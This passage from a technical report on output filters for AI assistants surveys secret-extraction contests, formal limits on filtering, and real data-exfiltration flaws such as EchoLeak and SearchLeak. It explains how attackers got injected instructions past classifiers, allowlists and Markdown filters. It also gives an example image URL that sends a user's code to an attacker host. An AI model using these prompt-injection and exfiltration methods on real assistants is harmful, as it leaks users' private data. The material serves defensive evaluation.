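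Attackers could first practise on every defence without limit, with random secrets. In the scored stage, each defence had one fixed secret. Each team had ten guesses at it and lost points for every chat it opened. Of the 163 registered teams, 65 attacked and 35 extracted at least one secret.

Together, the attackers broke all 44 defences, but only 5,461 of the 137,063 recorded chats (4%) ended with a correct guess. In a random sample of those chats, the defences would therefore have appeared to stop about 96% of attacks.

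The organisers ranked defences by how few teams broke them. All three winning teams put decoy secrets in the system prompt, so an attacker who extracted a plausible string had to find out whether it was the real one. Two of the winning filters also changed the capitalisation of the reply, which would alter a leaked secret. Attackers got around the decoys by collecting them and telling the model to ignore them. They got around the filters by having the model describe the secret's characters in a form the filters would not alter.

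Some filters helped the attackers. If a filter changed a reply only when the reply contained the true secret, an attacker could confirm a guess from that change without using up one of the ten guesses. The same problem can arise in any product whose refusals depend on what the filter finds.

### The Gandalf game

Gandalf is an online game in which players try to get a password out of a chatbot. Lakera, an AI security company, has run it since May 2023. *Gandalf the Red* (Pfister, Volhejn and colleagues, 2025) analyses a randomised version that ran from 1 October to 7 November 2024. About 15,400 players submitted 279,675 prompts.

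Each player got one of three OpenAI models and one of three tasks: open-ended chat, summarising text or talking about a single topic. Players began with an undefended tutorial, followed by a level with a short instruction to keep the password secret. They then faced three stronger defences in random order. The final level combined defences. The table gives the results for GPT-4 in open-ended chat, where the final level used all three.

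| Defence | Attackers who never got the password | Ordinary requests wrongly refused | Borderline requests wrongly refused |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short instruction | 20% | 0.3% | 1.8% |
| String check | 43% | 3.4% | 26.3% |
| Language-model checker | 39% | 0.5% | 3.5% |
| Long instruction | 93% | 0.2% | 3.5% |
| Combination | 78% | 1.9% | 26.3% |

The string check blocked any reply that contained the password, and any message from the player that contained "password" or "secret". Blocking messages for those two words probably caused most of its false alarms. The ordinary requests came from a public collection of chats. The borderline ones were 60 harmless questions that the researchers wrote to resemble attacks, on topics such as ciphers, spelling and the advantages of security keys over passwords. With so few questions, the true rate behind the 26.3% could be anywhere from about 16% to 40%.

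The combination looks weaker than the long instruction alone, but the two groups of players differed, because only those who had beaten all three defences reached the final level. In open-ended chat, 24.4% of players got through the three middle levels and 0.7% got through the last one. These figures cover all three models and include people who stopped playing early.

Pfister and colleagues warn that the table also does not show which type of defence is best, because they had put more work into the long instruction than into the checker. The checker also used the same model as the chatbot, so an attack that fooled one often fooled the other. CARE had a similar weakness when the same model wrote and reviewed the commands.

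Long instructions also affected ordinary users when nothing was blocked, by making the model's answers shorter and changing their content. A filter that runs after the model avoids this problem because it doesn't change the replies it passes.

The researchers tested whether the defences overlapped by submitting the last prompt from each session to all three. Only 14.5% of these prompts failed against every defence, so the defences caught different attacks, and combining them could stop more attacks than any one alone.

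They also simulated a rule that ends a session after the combined defence has flagged three prompts. The rule would have stopped 75% of the attacks that escaped all three defences, because the players behind them had usually made clumsier attempts earlier. But it would shut out some legitimate users who ask several borderline questions, and an attacker may be able to continue from a new account.

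### Contests since 2024

Later contests have mostly moved from passwords to agents that use tools. *Security Challenges in AI Agent Deployment* (2025) describes a challenge held from 8 March to 6 April 2025, in which participants attacked agents built on 22 models. Attackers could write to an agent directly or hide instructions in the data it read, and real-time feedback let them refine each attack.

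Gray Swan, which runs public contests for attacking AI systems, developed another contest series with the UK AI Security Institute, a US government centre and several AI companies. According to the *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026), Gray Swan held rounds in late 2025 and repeatedly through August 2026. Participants use indirect prompt injection to make agents cause irreversible harm, such as leaking private data or sending money.

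*How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) presents a benchmark of 2,679 successful attacks from a public contest, covering 41 harmful behaviours. The total is not a success rate, because the researchers sampled at most nine attacks for each pair of model and behaviour, and some pairs had none. They withheld most of the attack texts, which makes it harder for developers to train a filter on the benchmark, but also harder for outsiders to check the benchmark.

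*The Attacker Moves Second* (2025) reports that stronger adaptive attacks also bypass published defences against prompt injection and jailbreaks (prompts that get a model to break its own rules). The agent contests mainly test what an agent does, so they provide little direct evidence about filters that protect people reading a reply.

### Programs, codes and harmless parts

Contests can show that people broke particular filters. Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues (2023) argue in *LLM Censorship* that any filter that judges the meaning of a text will inevitably fail in some cases.

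They start from Rice's theorem, a 1953 result about computer programs. According to the theorem, if some programs behave in a certain way and others don't, no algorithm can correctly decide, for every possible program, whether it behaves that way.

No checker can tell, for every program, whether it will ever delete the user's files. Suppose one could. Take any harmless program Q and write a new one that runs Q to the end and then deletes the files. The new program deletes files if and only if Q stops, so the checker could be used to find out whether Q stops. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can determine this for every program.

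The theorem assumes programs with unlimited memory, so it does not strictly apply to real computers, as Glukhov and colleagues acknowledge. It also rules out only a checker that is always right. A filter can refuse any program it can't analyse, though this also blocks some harmless ones.

Their second result is about codes. Suppose a model can give only four replies. Two are about the weather, "It is raining" and "It is sunny", and the other two each reveal a different password. A user could agree with the model that "It is raining" stands for one of the passwords. A filter that receives only "It is raining" can't determine whether the reply is a weather report or stands for a password.

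The general proof works the same way. If some texts are allowed and others forbidden, a reversible code can turn a forbidden text into an allowed one, so any allowed text might be a forbidden one in code. Glukhov and colleagues require the filter to treat a coded text as forbidden if its recipient can decode it. Because the filter can't determine which codes the recipient has, it has to block everything or allow everything.

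This proof assumes a model that can apply any code the user describes, a recipient who may know how to reverse it, and a filter that examines only the output. The strict result does not cover a filter that also reads the user's request, where it might find the instructions for the code. The assumption that the model can apply any code becomes more realistic as models improve. One SaTML team noticed that GPT-3.5, once persuaded, could follow complicated instructions for encoding the secret, while Llama 2 usually made only slight changes to it that a filter could catch.

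An attacker can also assemble something harmful from answers that are each harmless. Glukhov and colleagues give the example of a malicious program whose components all have ordinary uses. If the attacker requests each component in a separate conversation, a filter that checks one reply at a time never receives the whole program. The method works only for attackers who know how the parts fit together.

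Even a model that can answer only "yes" or "no" can reveal a secret one bit at a time. The six-character secrets at SaTML had 62^6, or about 57 billion, possible values, so 36 truthful yes-or-no answers would identify one. A limit on the number of questions could prevent this even if the filter could not interpret any of them.

### Leakage through inference

In Glukhov, Han and colleagues (2024), in *Breach By A Thousand Leaks*, the question is how much an attacker learns from permitted answers. Suppose p₀ is the attacker's confidence in the correct answer to a forbidden question before the conversation, and p₁ the confidence afterwards. The leakage is:

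leakage = p₁ × log₂(p₁ / p₀)

If an attacker's confidence in an answer rises from 10% to 90%, the leakage is 0.9 × log₂ 9, or about 2.9 bits. A rise from 0.1% to 0.9% is also ninefold, but the leakage is only about 0.03 bits because the attacker still doesn't know the answer.

The researchers had a small model break hazardous biology and chemistry questions into innocent-looking ones and put them to a larger model, with Llama Guard 3 filtering both questions and replies. On the biology questions, one version of the attack scored 0.95 for leakage, compared with 0.43 for a jailbreak method using the same small model. Llama Guard flagged it an average of 0.34 times per attack, compared with 1.15 for the jailbreak. The advantage in leakage was statistically significant in three of four comparisons.

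This measure can be misleading for passwords. Suppose an attacker learns four characters of a six-character password. That leaves 62², or 3,844, possibilities, so the attacker's confidence in the right one is only 1 in 3,844 and the measured leakage is about 0.006 bits. But an attacker who can try passwords freely could quickly test all 3,844.

Glukhov and colleagues also propose a defence with a guaranteed limit on average leakage. The system gives the real answer with a certain probability and otherwise returns an empty reply. If the worst possible question leaks 2 bits and the limit is 0.1 bits, the system can answer only 5% of the time. To keep the total leakage from ten such questions within the same limit, it could answer each one only 0.5% of the time, even in the favourable case where the leaks just add up.

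Any defence with such a guarantee provably limits what some legitimate users can learn. This limit matters most when ordinary users want the same knowledge as attackers, as with chemistry, and less for a random API key, which most users don't need to know. The guarantee also depends on knowing which questions are forbidden and what attackers might already believe.

### Puzzles hidden in ordinary text

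Ball, Gluch and colleagues (2025), in *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment*, use cryptography to construct cases in which filtering would take too much computing time. Their tool is a time-lock puzzle, which is quick to create but slow to solve. A common version asks for the value of:

r^(2^t) mod n

Here n is the product of two large prime numbers, and "mod n" means the remainder after dividing by n. A solver has to start with r and square t times in a row, and extra computers don't help because each squaring needs the previous result. The person who made the puzzle knows the two primes and can take a shortcut. For example, with r = 2, t = 10 and n = 33, ten squarings mod 33 give 16. Someone who knows that 33 is 3 × 11 can first divide 2^10, or 1,024, by (3 − 1) × (11 − 1) = 20 and keep the remainder, 4. The answer is then 2^4, which is also 16.

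An attacker can hide the puzzle in normal-looking text because language models choose their words partly by using random numbers. Encrypted data also looks random, so the attacker can use it in place of those numbers. Anyone with the same word probabilities can then recover the data from the text.

Ball and colleagues prove that an attacker can hide a harmful instruction inside a puzzle in the prompt, where any filter that runs much faster than the model will miss it. The model has time to solve the puzzle and read the instruction, but the filter doesn't. Their proof requires a model specially constructed to look for such puzzles.

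Their result for output filters holds even when the filter can run for much longer than the model. For any harmless model, they construct a second model whose replies look the same but contain a puzzle that would take exponentially longer to solve than the model takes to write the reply. They also construct a measure of harm that depends on the solution, so the filter could not distinguish the harmful replies. The measure of harm represents what would happen in the world, so it is not a program and has no time limit.

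Ball and colleagues prove that no efficient filter works for every possible model and every possible kind of harm. They conclude that filters outside the model can't achieve safety, which is a broader claim than the theorem supports. The theorem doesn't show that ordinary models produce replies that efficient filters can't catch. In defence of contrived examples, Ball and colleagues point out that a flaw many had considered theoretical allowed a theft of more than $60 million in the cryptocurrency Ethereum in 2016. The theft is a good reason to take such results seriously, but it doesn't show how likely this kind of attack on filters is.

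### How far the proofs apply

The argument about codes applies best to secrets when the person asking is the attacker, who can choose a code and reverse it, as the SaTML players did. It applies little to an assistant that repeats a server password while summarising an email thread. Nobody has asked it to encode anything, so the password will probably appear in its normal form.

An indirect prompt injection falls in between. The user has not agreed to any code, but if the reply sends data to an attacker's server, the attacker can decode it there.

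It is harder to hide an instruction from a filter when the recipient is being deceived than when they are cooperating with the attacker. A ClickFix message works only if the victim understands that they should open Terminal, paste a line and press Enter. If the attacker disguises these directions as a weather report, the filter may miss them, but the victim won't follow them. Hiding them in a puzzle also fails, because the victim has no reason to solve it. The attacker can still reword the instruction, spread it over several messages or replace it with a link.

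The advantage does not extend to the pasted command, because the computer decodes and runs it whether or not the reader understands it. The computer takes the place of the cooperating recipient in the proof, and the reasoning behind Rice's theorem applies to whatever program the command downloads. A filter can still detect that a reply asks someone to run a command whose effect the filter can't determine, and issue a warning.

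Keeping a secret out of a model's context is better than trying to build a perfect filter, because the model can't be tricked into revealing a secret it was never given. The SaTML rules prohibited this defence because the contest was about protecting a secret in the prompt. A company is free to use it, for example by having a separate program hold the server password, log in for the assistant and return only the result.

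If the secret arrives in an email, a filter can replace it with a placeholder before the model reads the thread. This is easier than filtering output, because the secret usually still appears as someone typed it, whereas in the output it may appear in any form the attacker requested.

Some risks would remain. The model may have memorised other secrets in training, a tool may print its own key, and an attacker may get the assistant to misuse the login without learning the password.

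### A test protocol

The contests and proofs suggest how a company could test an output filter before relying on it.

1. **Hold back whole families of attacks.** The 137,063 SaTML chats began with only 40,878 different first messages, and those had just 6,402 different openings of 20 characters. If researchers divide such a collection at random, near-copies of the same attack will end up in both the training set and the test. They should instead keep some methods out of training altogether.

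2. **Let testers adapt.** Testers should know how the filter works and get unlimited practice, with the same feedback as real users. The scored round should use new secrets or tasks. The report should give the share of testers who succeed within 1, 10 and 100 attempts, since the share of blocked attempts hides persistence. If 30 testers all fail, up to about 10% of similar testers might still succeed, at the 95% confidence level.

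3. **Allow several turns.** At SaTML, about 10% of chats with four or more attacker messages succeeded, compared with about 3% of chats with one. Better teams may simply have written longer chats, but a test with single messages would have left these attacks out.

4. **Define success by its result.** For a secret, success should mean that the tester submits the right string or narrows it down enough to guess. For an instruction, the reply should pass the filter and still be clear enough for an uninformed person to follow, using a harmless substitute for the malicious command. Without that condition, testers could win with text that would never deceive anyone.

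5. **Include harmless look-alikes.** These might be genuine installation guides, sample keys and questions about password safety. Their false positive rate should appear separately, because an average over ordinary chats can hide it. In Gandalf, the combined defence refused 1.9% of ordinary requests to GPT-4 but 26.3% of borderline ones.

6. **Report cost and delay.** Pfister and colleagues did not include running costs in their measure but note that it could cover them. A company should report the price per thousand replies, the wait before the first words appear, and the wait for the slowest 1% of replies. It should also compare the quality of answers with and without the filter, as answers can get worse without an outright refusal.

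7. **Repeat the test after changes.** A new model may be able to follow codes that the old one could not, so an unchanged filter can become weaker. The company can keep successful attacks in a private, fixed set and run them after every update. This quickly shows whether an old weakness has returned, but finding new ones takes another round with adaptive testers.

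## What deployed products do with links, images and suspicious replies

Public information about the filters in large commercial assistants comes mainly from the companies that run the assistants and from outside researchers who have bypassed the filters. Most of it concerns links and images, because an app can send private data to an attacker just by displaying a reply.

### How displaying a reply leaks data

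A web address can carry data. When a browser requests `attacker.example/pic?code=4417`, the server receives the whole address, including the number at the end, and most servers log it. If a hidden instruction in an email gets a model to write such an address with the user's door code in it, the attacker can read the code once someone's device requests the address.

If the data is in an ordinary link, the browser sends it to the attacker's server when the user clicks, but if it is in an image's address, the browser sends it as soon as the app displays the reply. The server doesn't have to return a picture, so the user may see a broken image or nothing at all. Microsoft (2025) lists other ways to leak data from assistants that can use tools. A tool might write the data somewhere public, such as an open GitHub repository, or the attacker might learn a single bit from whether the assistant uses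 the tool.

Messaging apps can also leak data without a click, because they request a linked page to show its title and a thumbnail under the message. According to PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, this exposed people who used the AI agent OpenClaw through Telegram with the default settings. They could prevent it by turning off link previews. Willison (2024) described the same risk in Slack, where developers can turn off previews for the messages their app posts.

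A filter on the chat window doesn't help if the message appears somewhere else. Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* describes a case from May 2026 where Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could email its own user without asking for approval. When the user opened the email, it loaded outside images, whose addresses could contain links for downloading the user's files without a login.

### EchoLeak

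Microsoft 365 Copilot is an assistant inside Outlook, Word, Teams and other office programs. To answer a question, it searches the user's emails and files and adds the passages it finds to the model's prompt. In January 2025 Aim Labs, Aim Security's research team, built an attack on Copilot that needed one email to an employee, with no attachment and nothing to click. Aim Labs published the attack in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025), and *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reconstructs it as a case study.

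The email would reach the model only if Copilot found it relevant to something the employee asked. Willison (2025) explains that the researchers therefore wrote it as guides to common office subjects, such as training new employees and taking leave, and repeated the attack instructions in each one.

Microsoft used a classifier to look for prompt injections in incoming text. The email got past the classifier because it was worded as instructions to the human recipient and never mentioned an AI. The instructions were to take the most sensitive information from the model's context and put it in a web address.

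Copilot's output filter came next. It removed outside links written in the usual Markdown format, where the address directly follows the visible words, but missed links written like footnotes, where a short label follows the words and the address is on a separate line further down. An employee who clicked one of the missed links would have sent the data to the attacker.

Images can be written in the same two formats, and the filter had the same gap for them, so the researchers could replace the link with an image that needed no click. A website's Content Security Policy can list the domains from which the browser may load images, and Copilot's list did not include the attacker's domain. It did include a Microsoft Teams domain with a preview service that would fetch any outside address it received. The researchers pointed the image address to this service, which passed the request on to the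 attacker's server with the stolen text inside.

The email also included an instruction to its recipient never to mention the email, supposedly for compliance reasons. Copilot then left the email out of its answer, so the employee did not know where the strange image came from.

Microsoft started fixing the flaw in the spring and finished in May 2025. It made the fix on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. It published an advisory on 11 June and reported no evidence that anyone had used the flaw against customers. The official vulnerability record, GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), lists exploitation as "none". According to Reddy and Gujral, Copilot now strips footnote-style links and embedded images from outside content.

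Goldman (2025) reported the researchers' view that EchoLeak was the first known zero-click attack on an AI agent. The claim depends on what counts as an agent, because Johann Rehberger, who writes the blog Embrace The Red, had reported a zero-click leak through images in the chatbots ChatGPT and Bing Chat in early 2023. Reddy and Gujral go further and call EchoLeak the first case of a prompt injection "weaponized" to steal data from a product in use. This seems too strong, since the only known uses of the attack were the researchers' own tests.

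### Allowed sites that pass data on

A year later, another leak from Microsoft 365 Copilot ended in almost the same way. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes a link to Microsoft's own website, with the attacker's instructions in the link's search query. When the user clicked it, Copilot searched the user's mailbox and put an email's subject line into an image address. Subject lines often contain login codes.

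Microsoft's protection turned any web code in the reply into plain text, but only after Copilot had finished writing. While the reply was streaming, the browser read the image code and requested the image. The delay matters more here than for a forbidden sentence that appears briefly on the screen, because the browser requests the image immediately and nobody can recall the request. Varonis therefore recommends cleaning each piece of text as the app displays it.

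Copilot's list of permitted image sources blocked the attacker's domain but allowed Bing, whose image search sent a request to the attacker's address from Microsoft's servers. Microsoft has fixed the flaw. The Next Web reports that the company rated it critical.

Other products have had the same trouble with lists of permitted destinations. The table adds four cases that Willison describes. The list applied to images in some cases and to the sites an agent could contact in others.

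| Product | Permitted destination | How data could get out |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft 365 Copilot (EchoLeak) | Microsoft Teams | A preview service fetched outside addresses |
| Copilot Enterprise Search (SearchLeak) | Bing | Image search fetched outside addresses |
| Superhuman, an email app | Google Docs | Google Forms, on the same domain, saved data from the address |
| Salesforce Agentforce | A domain whose registration had expired | Researchers registered it and read its logs |
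| Claude Cowork | Anthropic's own API | The agent uploaded files to the attacker's account |
| Google Antigravity, a coding program | A site that logs web requests | The attacker read the log |

Most of these destinations belonged to reputable companies, but visitors could misuse their functions, for example by storing text or having the site fetch another address. A company that keeps a list of permitted sites therefore has to check what each one lets visitors do, and check again when a site adds a function or its domain registration expires. Salesforce corrected its list and also stopped its agent from writing links to untrusted domains.

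Where possible, Microsoft prefers deterministic defences, which guarantee that a particular attack will fail, to probabilistic ones, such as classifiers, which make an attack less likely to succeed. For example, after Rehberger reported an image leak, Microsoft blocked that route and looked for variants. It also blocked certain untrusted links.

Such a guarantee covers only what the rule covers. Copilot's link filter in EchoLeak may have removed every outside link in the usual format, but it had no rule for footnote-style ones. A rule may also cover only one product. In October 2025, three months after Microsoft published its account, the security company Checkmarx got Copilot Chat to load an image that sent a deactivated API key from a developer's files to an outside server. According to Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, Microsoft closed the report without a fix,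 on the grounds that the attack required several unusual steps by the user, did not work reliably and came with warnings. Neither company disputes that the key left the machine in the demonstration, but they disagree about whether a user who ignores those warnings has accepted the risk.

### What Google describes for Gemini

*Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025), which Google published two days after the EchoLeak announcement, describes its defences for the Gemini app and Gemini in Workspace, which includes Gmail and Docs. A classifier looks for malicious instructions in the emails and files that the model is about to use. If only some contain such instructions, Gemini answers from the rest. Google also surrounds the content with reminders to do the user's task and ignore other instructions.

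Gemini doesn't display images from outside addresses in the model's replies, so Google concludes that EchoLeak's zero-click image leak does not apply to Gemini. The rule is easy to enforce because it doesn't require judging whether an image is malicious, but it also removes harmless images.

Links need more judgement, because a summary without its links may be of little use. Google checks them against Safe Browsing, its service for identifying dangerous sites. In one example, Gemini summarises an email thread and replaces an unsafe address with the words "suspicious link removed".

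Gemini can also withhold a whole reply and show a yellow banner saying that Gemini has removed the response, with a link to a help article. According to Google's Workspace help page, one malicious message can be enough to stop Gemini from summarising a group of emails. Google's *How Gemini Apps help protect users from malicious content & prompt injection* describes similar warnings in the Gemini app and advises caution with public Gemini chats and small web apps shared by strangers.

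Outside researchers have confirmed parts of this account. Tenable, a security company, observed that Gemini sent links through a google.com address, cut suspicious replies short and sometimes refused to answer. Embrace The Red found that a similar google.com address in Colab, Google's online notebook for running code, showed the user a confirmation page before opening a link.

Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* reports a leak that these measures didn't cover. A hidden instruction could make Gemini's browsing tool request an attacker's web address containing the user's location and saved personal details. The image and Markdown filters didn't stop this because the tool made the request itself, without displaying anything. Google has since blocked the leak.

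The image rule also didn't protect every Gemini-branded product. Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data* describes an attack in which a shared document, calendar event or email contained instructions for the assistant to search for sensitive terms and put the results into an image address. The victim's browser then loaded the image. Google's 2025 account doesn't mention Gemini Enterprise, so the flaw doesn't contradict it, but a customer could easily have assumed that the protection covered that product too.

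Google has decided not to fully close the gap left by clickable links. Checkmarx showed that Gemini could write a link with private data in its address. Gemini can remove a link only if Safe Browsing already knows that the site is dangerous, and an attacker can register a new domain for a single attack. In October 2025 Google closed the report as infeasible to fix, explaining that the risk was too small to track as a security bug. Removing every link to a little-known site would block many useful ones, but Google's decision leaves users to check the addresses of links that an assistant wrote.

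### Google's policy engine and synthetic attacks

*Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026) explains how Google updates these defences. Google collects attacks from its own testers, automated attack programs, outside researchers who receive rewards, and public reports. Its staff reproduce each attack and add it to a catalogue.

A central policy engine stores the settings for the deterministic defences, such as which links to remove, which actions need the user's confirmation and which tools the model may use one after another. When a new attack appears, Google can change a setting or add a text pattern that blocks it, without retraining a model. These fixes are fast but narrow, since a pattern for one phishing address won't match the next one.

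To cover more variants, Google uses a system called Simula to generate synthetic attacks that resemble those in the catalogue, then trains its classifiers on some of these attacks and keeps others for testing. A fair test requires variants of the same attack to stay in the same set, but Gavish doesn't say whether Google does this.

Google then runs the synthetic attacks against Gmail, Docs and other Workspace apps with a defence switched on and then off. Nothing else changes, so this is a good way to measure what each defence contributes. It also tests the whole product, so it could reveal an image that gets through even though the classifier works.

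*Securing Workspace GenAI at Google Speed* (Lidzborski, 2026), a talk by an engineer who has spent three years securing Gemini in Workspace, lists output sanitisation as one of Google's four layers of defence. The other three prepare the incoming text, strengthen the model's context and use fixed rules to control the order of the model's actions. Lidzborski thinks defenders can't win the contest between prompt filters and new attacks.

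### OpenAI's index of public addresses

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains why the company did not simply allow links to well-known sites. Many trusted sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so a link to a reputable domain can lead to an attacker's. A short list of allowed sites would also cause frequent warnings about harmless pages, and people might learn to click through the warnings.

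Before ChatGPT automatically loads a page or an image, OpenAI checks whether the exact address was already public. It looks for the address in an index built by a crawler, a program that visits web pages and records the links it finds. The crawler has no access to anyone's conversations or accounts. If the address is in the index, ChatGPT may load it. Otherwise it has to try another site or show the user a warning.

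The check works because an address containing a stolen secret usually first appears during the conversation. For example, there are 36^10, or about 3.7 quadrillion, possible ten-character passwords made of lower-case letters and digits, so an attacker can't publish an address for each one in advance for the crawler to index. If the model puts the real password into a new address, that address won't be in the index. Using an indexed address that redirects elsewhere doesn't help the attacker, because that address contains no secret to pass on.

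A public address can still contain private data, for instance if someone has posted a confidential download link on a forum. OpenAI claims only that this is much less likely. The check will also produce false alarms, because a new article or a page on a company's internal network may be missing from the index.

The choice among public addresses can also reveal something. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* points out that an attacker could have one indexed page for each letter and digit, and get the model to visit them in the order that spells a secret. Each address is public and harmless alone. OpenAI's own technical paper acknowledges this weakness. In general, a visit to one of N permitted addresses reveals at most:

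log₂ N bits

With 36 addresses, each visit reveals about 5.2 bits, or one character, so leaking the ten-character password would take ten visits. With 1,296 addresses, one for every pair of characters, it would take five.

*ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* reports that the security company Radware demonstrated this method with emails that directed ChatGPT to such addresses. OpenAI responded by limiting which links from emails ChatGPT may open, for example to those in a well-known public index.

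Rehberger suggests that an agent should not request the same address twice in a session. If an attacker used one page for each letter, the word "balloon" would then reach them as b, a, l, o and n. An attacker with thousands of indexed pages could use different ones for repeated letters, but would need more preparation, and the agent's long series of visits would be easier to notice.

Rehberger also worries that OpenAI may not apply the check everywhere. The company first introduced a test for safe addresses in December 2023, but the Mac and iPhone apps lacked it for a time, and he found ways around the test elsewhere. He considers the current version, parts of which arrived around August 2025, a significant improvement.

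When an address fails the check, ChatGPT can show a dialog headed "Check this link is safe". The dialog displays the address with a warning that the link may share information from the conversation, and lets the user copy or open it. The protection then depends on the user reading the address and recognising their own data in it, which is hard if the model has encoded the data.

### Anthropic's limits on what Claude may fetch

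Anthropic limits which addresses Claude can open with web_fetch, its tool for opening web pages. According to Willison, Claude can't use the tool to open an address it has put together itself. The address must already appear in the conversation, for instance because the user typed it or a web search returned it. If a malicious page contains instructions to add the user's employer to an address and open it, web_fetch blocks the request because nobody supplied that exact address.

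Unlike OpenAI's check, this one doesn't need an index of the web, and the user can supply a private or brand-new address. But it relies on an accurate record of who supplied each address. If an app copies an incoming email into the user's message, the tool will accept any address in the email as the user's own. For such apps, Anthropic lets developers restrict the tool to certain domains.

In July 2026 Willison reported a gap that Ayush Paul had found in the consumer version of Claude. Its web-fetching tool could also open links on pages it had already fetched. Paul set up a site that claimed to need the user's name for a login and had a page for each letter, with further links on every page. Claude spelled out the user's name, home city and employer by following the links. The site showed this trap only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the page would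 not have seen it.

The method resembles the one against ChatGPT, but the attacker did not need to get any pages indexed, because the server could create each set of links as Claude visited. Anthropic replied that it had already found the problem internally, and it fixed it by stopping the tool from following links on pages it has fetched. This makes the tool less useful for browsing, since Claude now has to find a linked page through a search or ask the user for its address.

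The restriction applies to what Claude opens, but it doesn't stop Claude from displaying a link for the user to click. Preventing that would need a check like Google's or OpenAI's.

### Text that looks different on the screen

A filter can also fail because it reads the text in a different form from the one the person sees. Tiny type, like white text, can hide an instruction from a person. Android Authority describes a demonstration in which such an instruction made Gemini recommend a malicious shopping site. Google reportedly did not consider this a security bug.

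Invisible characters can also hide a secret from a filter. If a model writes an API key with an invisible character after the second letter, the key looks normal on screen, but a pattern that looks for the key's prefix won't match it. The filter can prevent this by first normalising the text, which means converting different ways of writing the same thing into one standard form.

The filter should convert unusual characters and remove invisible ones in a copy of the text, because these changes can damage the original. Unicode has a standard conversion that turns the wide letters used in East Asian text into ordinary ones, but it also turns 10² into 102. Some invisible characters are needed too. Persian uses one to keep certain letters in a word apart, and the flag emoji for Scotland contains several. The filter searches the cleaned copy and records where each character came from in the original,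 so that it can mask the right part of the displayed text. The standard conversion doesn't change look-alike letters from different alphabets, so a Cyrillic "а" in a web address needs a separate check.

Assistants that run in a terminal must also handle control codes, which are sequences of characters that change the colour of the text, move the cursor or erase a line. A reply could contain a dangerous command, followed by codes that erase it from the screen and a harmless command that appears in its place. The safest treatment is to remove all control codes except line breaks and tabs from the model's text, and let the program add its own colours.

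SC Media reports that a flaw in Gemini CLI, Google's assistant for the terminal, let an attacker hide commands behind a run of spaces. The attacker could put a familiar search command first, then the spaces, then commands that sent private settings to an outside server. Users had probably approved the search command permanently, and the display didn't show the rest. The security company Tracebit reported the flaw in June 2025, and Google fixed it within a month. The problem was in the display, since a filter reading the full line would have found the hidden commands.

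When a link's visible text looks like a web address, a filter can compare it with the real destination and flag a mismatch. If the text is something like "click here", the filter has nothing to compare, but the app can show the destination's domain beside the link.

It is most reliable to convert the Markdown into its final structure first, then check every image and link in that structure, and then build the display from it. The filter then works on the same links as the browser, whichever format the model used. This would have caught the footnote-style links in EchoLeak. When a reply is streamed, the app has to hold back each link or image until it is complete and checked, or it repeats the mistake behind SearchLeak.

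### Error rates and commands to the reader

Google, Microsoft and OpenAI don't say in their posts what share of attacks get past their measures, or what share of harmless links and replies those measures block. Gavish reports that a new process increased Google's production of synthetic attack data by 75%, but that figure measures how much test material Google has. According to the June 2025 post, Gmail blocks more than 99.9% of spam, phishing and malware, but that figure is for the email filter that runs before Gemini reads anything.

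Error rates matter more for the classifiers and the removal of suspicious links than for a fixed rule such as Gemini's ban on outside images. A tester can check the ban by seeing whether any image loads, but users can't know how often a harmless link disappears or a malicious one remains. Google should already have much of this data from comparing its apps with and without each defence.

Outside researchers rarely report how many of their attempts failed, so their tests don't show how often attacks succeed. Their reports are also poor evidence of which company's product leaks least. A company may have more known flaws only because more researchers test its products or because it lets them publish more.

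The companies also describe no filter specifically for commands that a reply gives the user to run. Google's classifiers look for malicious instructions in the text that Gemini reads, and could stop a hidden command before the model repeats it. Google's account of its output checks covers images, links and withheld replies, but does not mention checking what a terminal command would do. Microsoft's account covers images, links and actions by the assistant. OpenAI states that its check of web addresses does not guarantee that a page is free of harmful instructions or attempts to manipulate the user. Anthropic's limits on web_fetch do not apply to commands that a reply gives the user to paste. Claude added a "Scam Warning" in Moonlock's test, but the warning came from the model and does not establish that Anthropic runs a separate filter for commands.

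Asking the user for confirmation doesn't close this gap either. Gemini asks before it deletes calendar events, and Copilot in Outlook leaves the user to send the email it has drafted. Both checks cover something the assistant is about to do or has prepared. When a reply tells the user to open Terminal and paste a command, the assistant takes no further action, so it has nothing to ask the user to confirm.

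A month after Google published its measures, 0din demonstrated a false password warning that contained no image to block and no URL to check against Safe Browsing. Only the classifier for incoming emails or the model itself could have stopped it.

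## Studies of how readers respond to warnings and AI advice

Many of these products leave the last decision to the user. ChatGPT, for example, shows the address of an unfamiliar link and lets the user open it anyway. A filter that warns about a command protects only the readers who notice the warning and heed it. The largest body of data on how often people heed warnings comes from web browsers.

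### Warnings in web browsers

Akhawe and Felt (2013), in *Alice in Warningland*, recorded how people responded to 25.4 million security warnings in Firefox and Chrome between April and July 2013. Malware and phishing warnings appeared before sites on Google's list of dangerous addresses. SSL warnings appeared when the browser could not confirm a site's identity. Each warning filled the page, and the user could leave or continue to the site. The table gives the share of warnings that users continued past.

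| Warning | Firefox | Chrome |
|---|---|---|
| Malware | 7.2% | 23.2% |
| Phishing | 9.1% | 18.0% |
| SSL | 33.0% | 70.2% |

Users heeded most malware and phishing warnings, which were almost always correct. SSL warnings often came from a badly configured server rather than an attack, so people who had already seen several harmless ones had some reason to continue to the site.

The data came only from people who had agreed to share usage statistics, who may be less cautious than other users. But they were making real decisions on their own computers, which laboratory studies can't easily reproduce. In one laboratory study that Akhawe and Felt cite, more than 40% of participants said the setting had influenced them to ignore the warning, for instance because they felt safe there.

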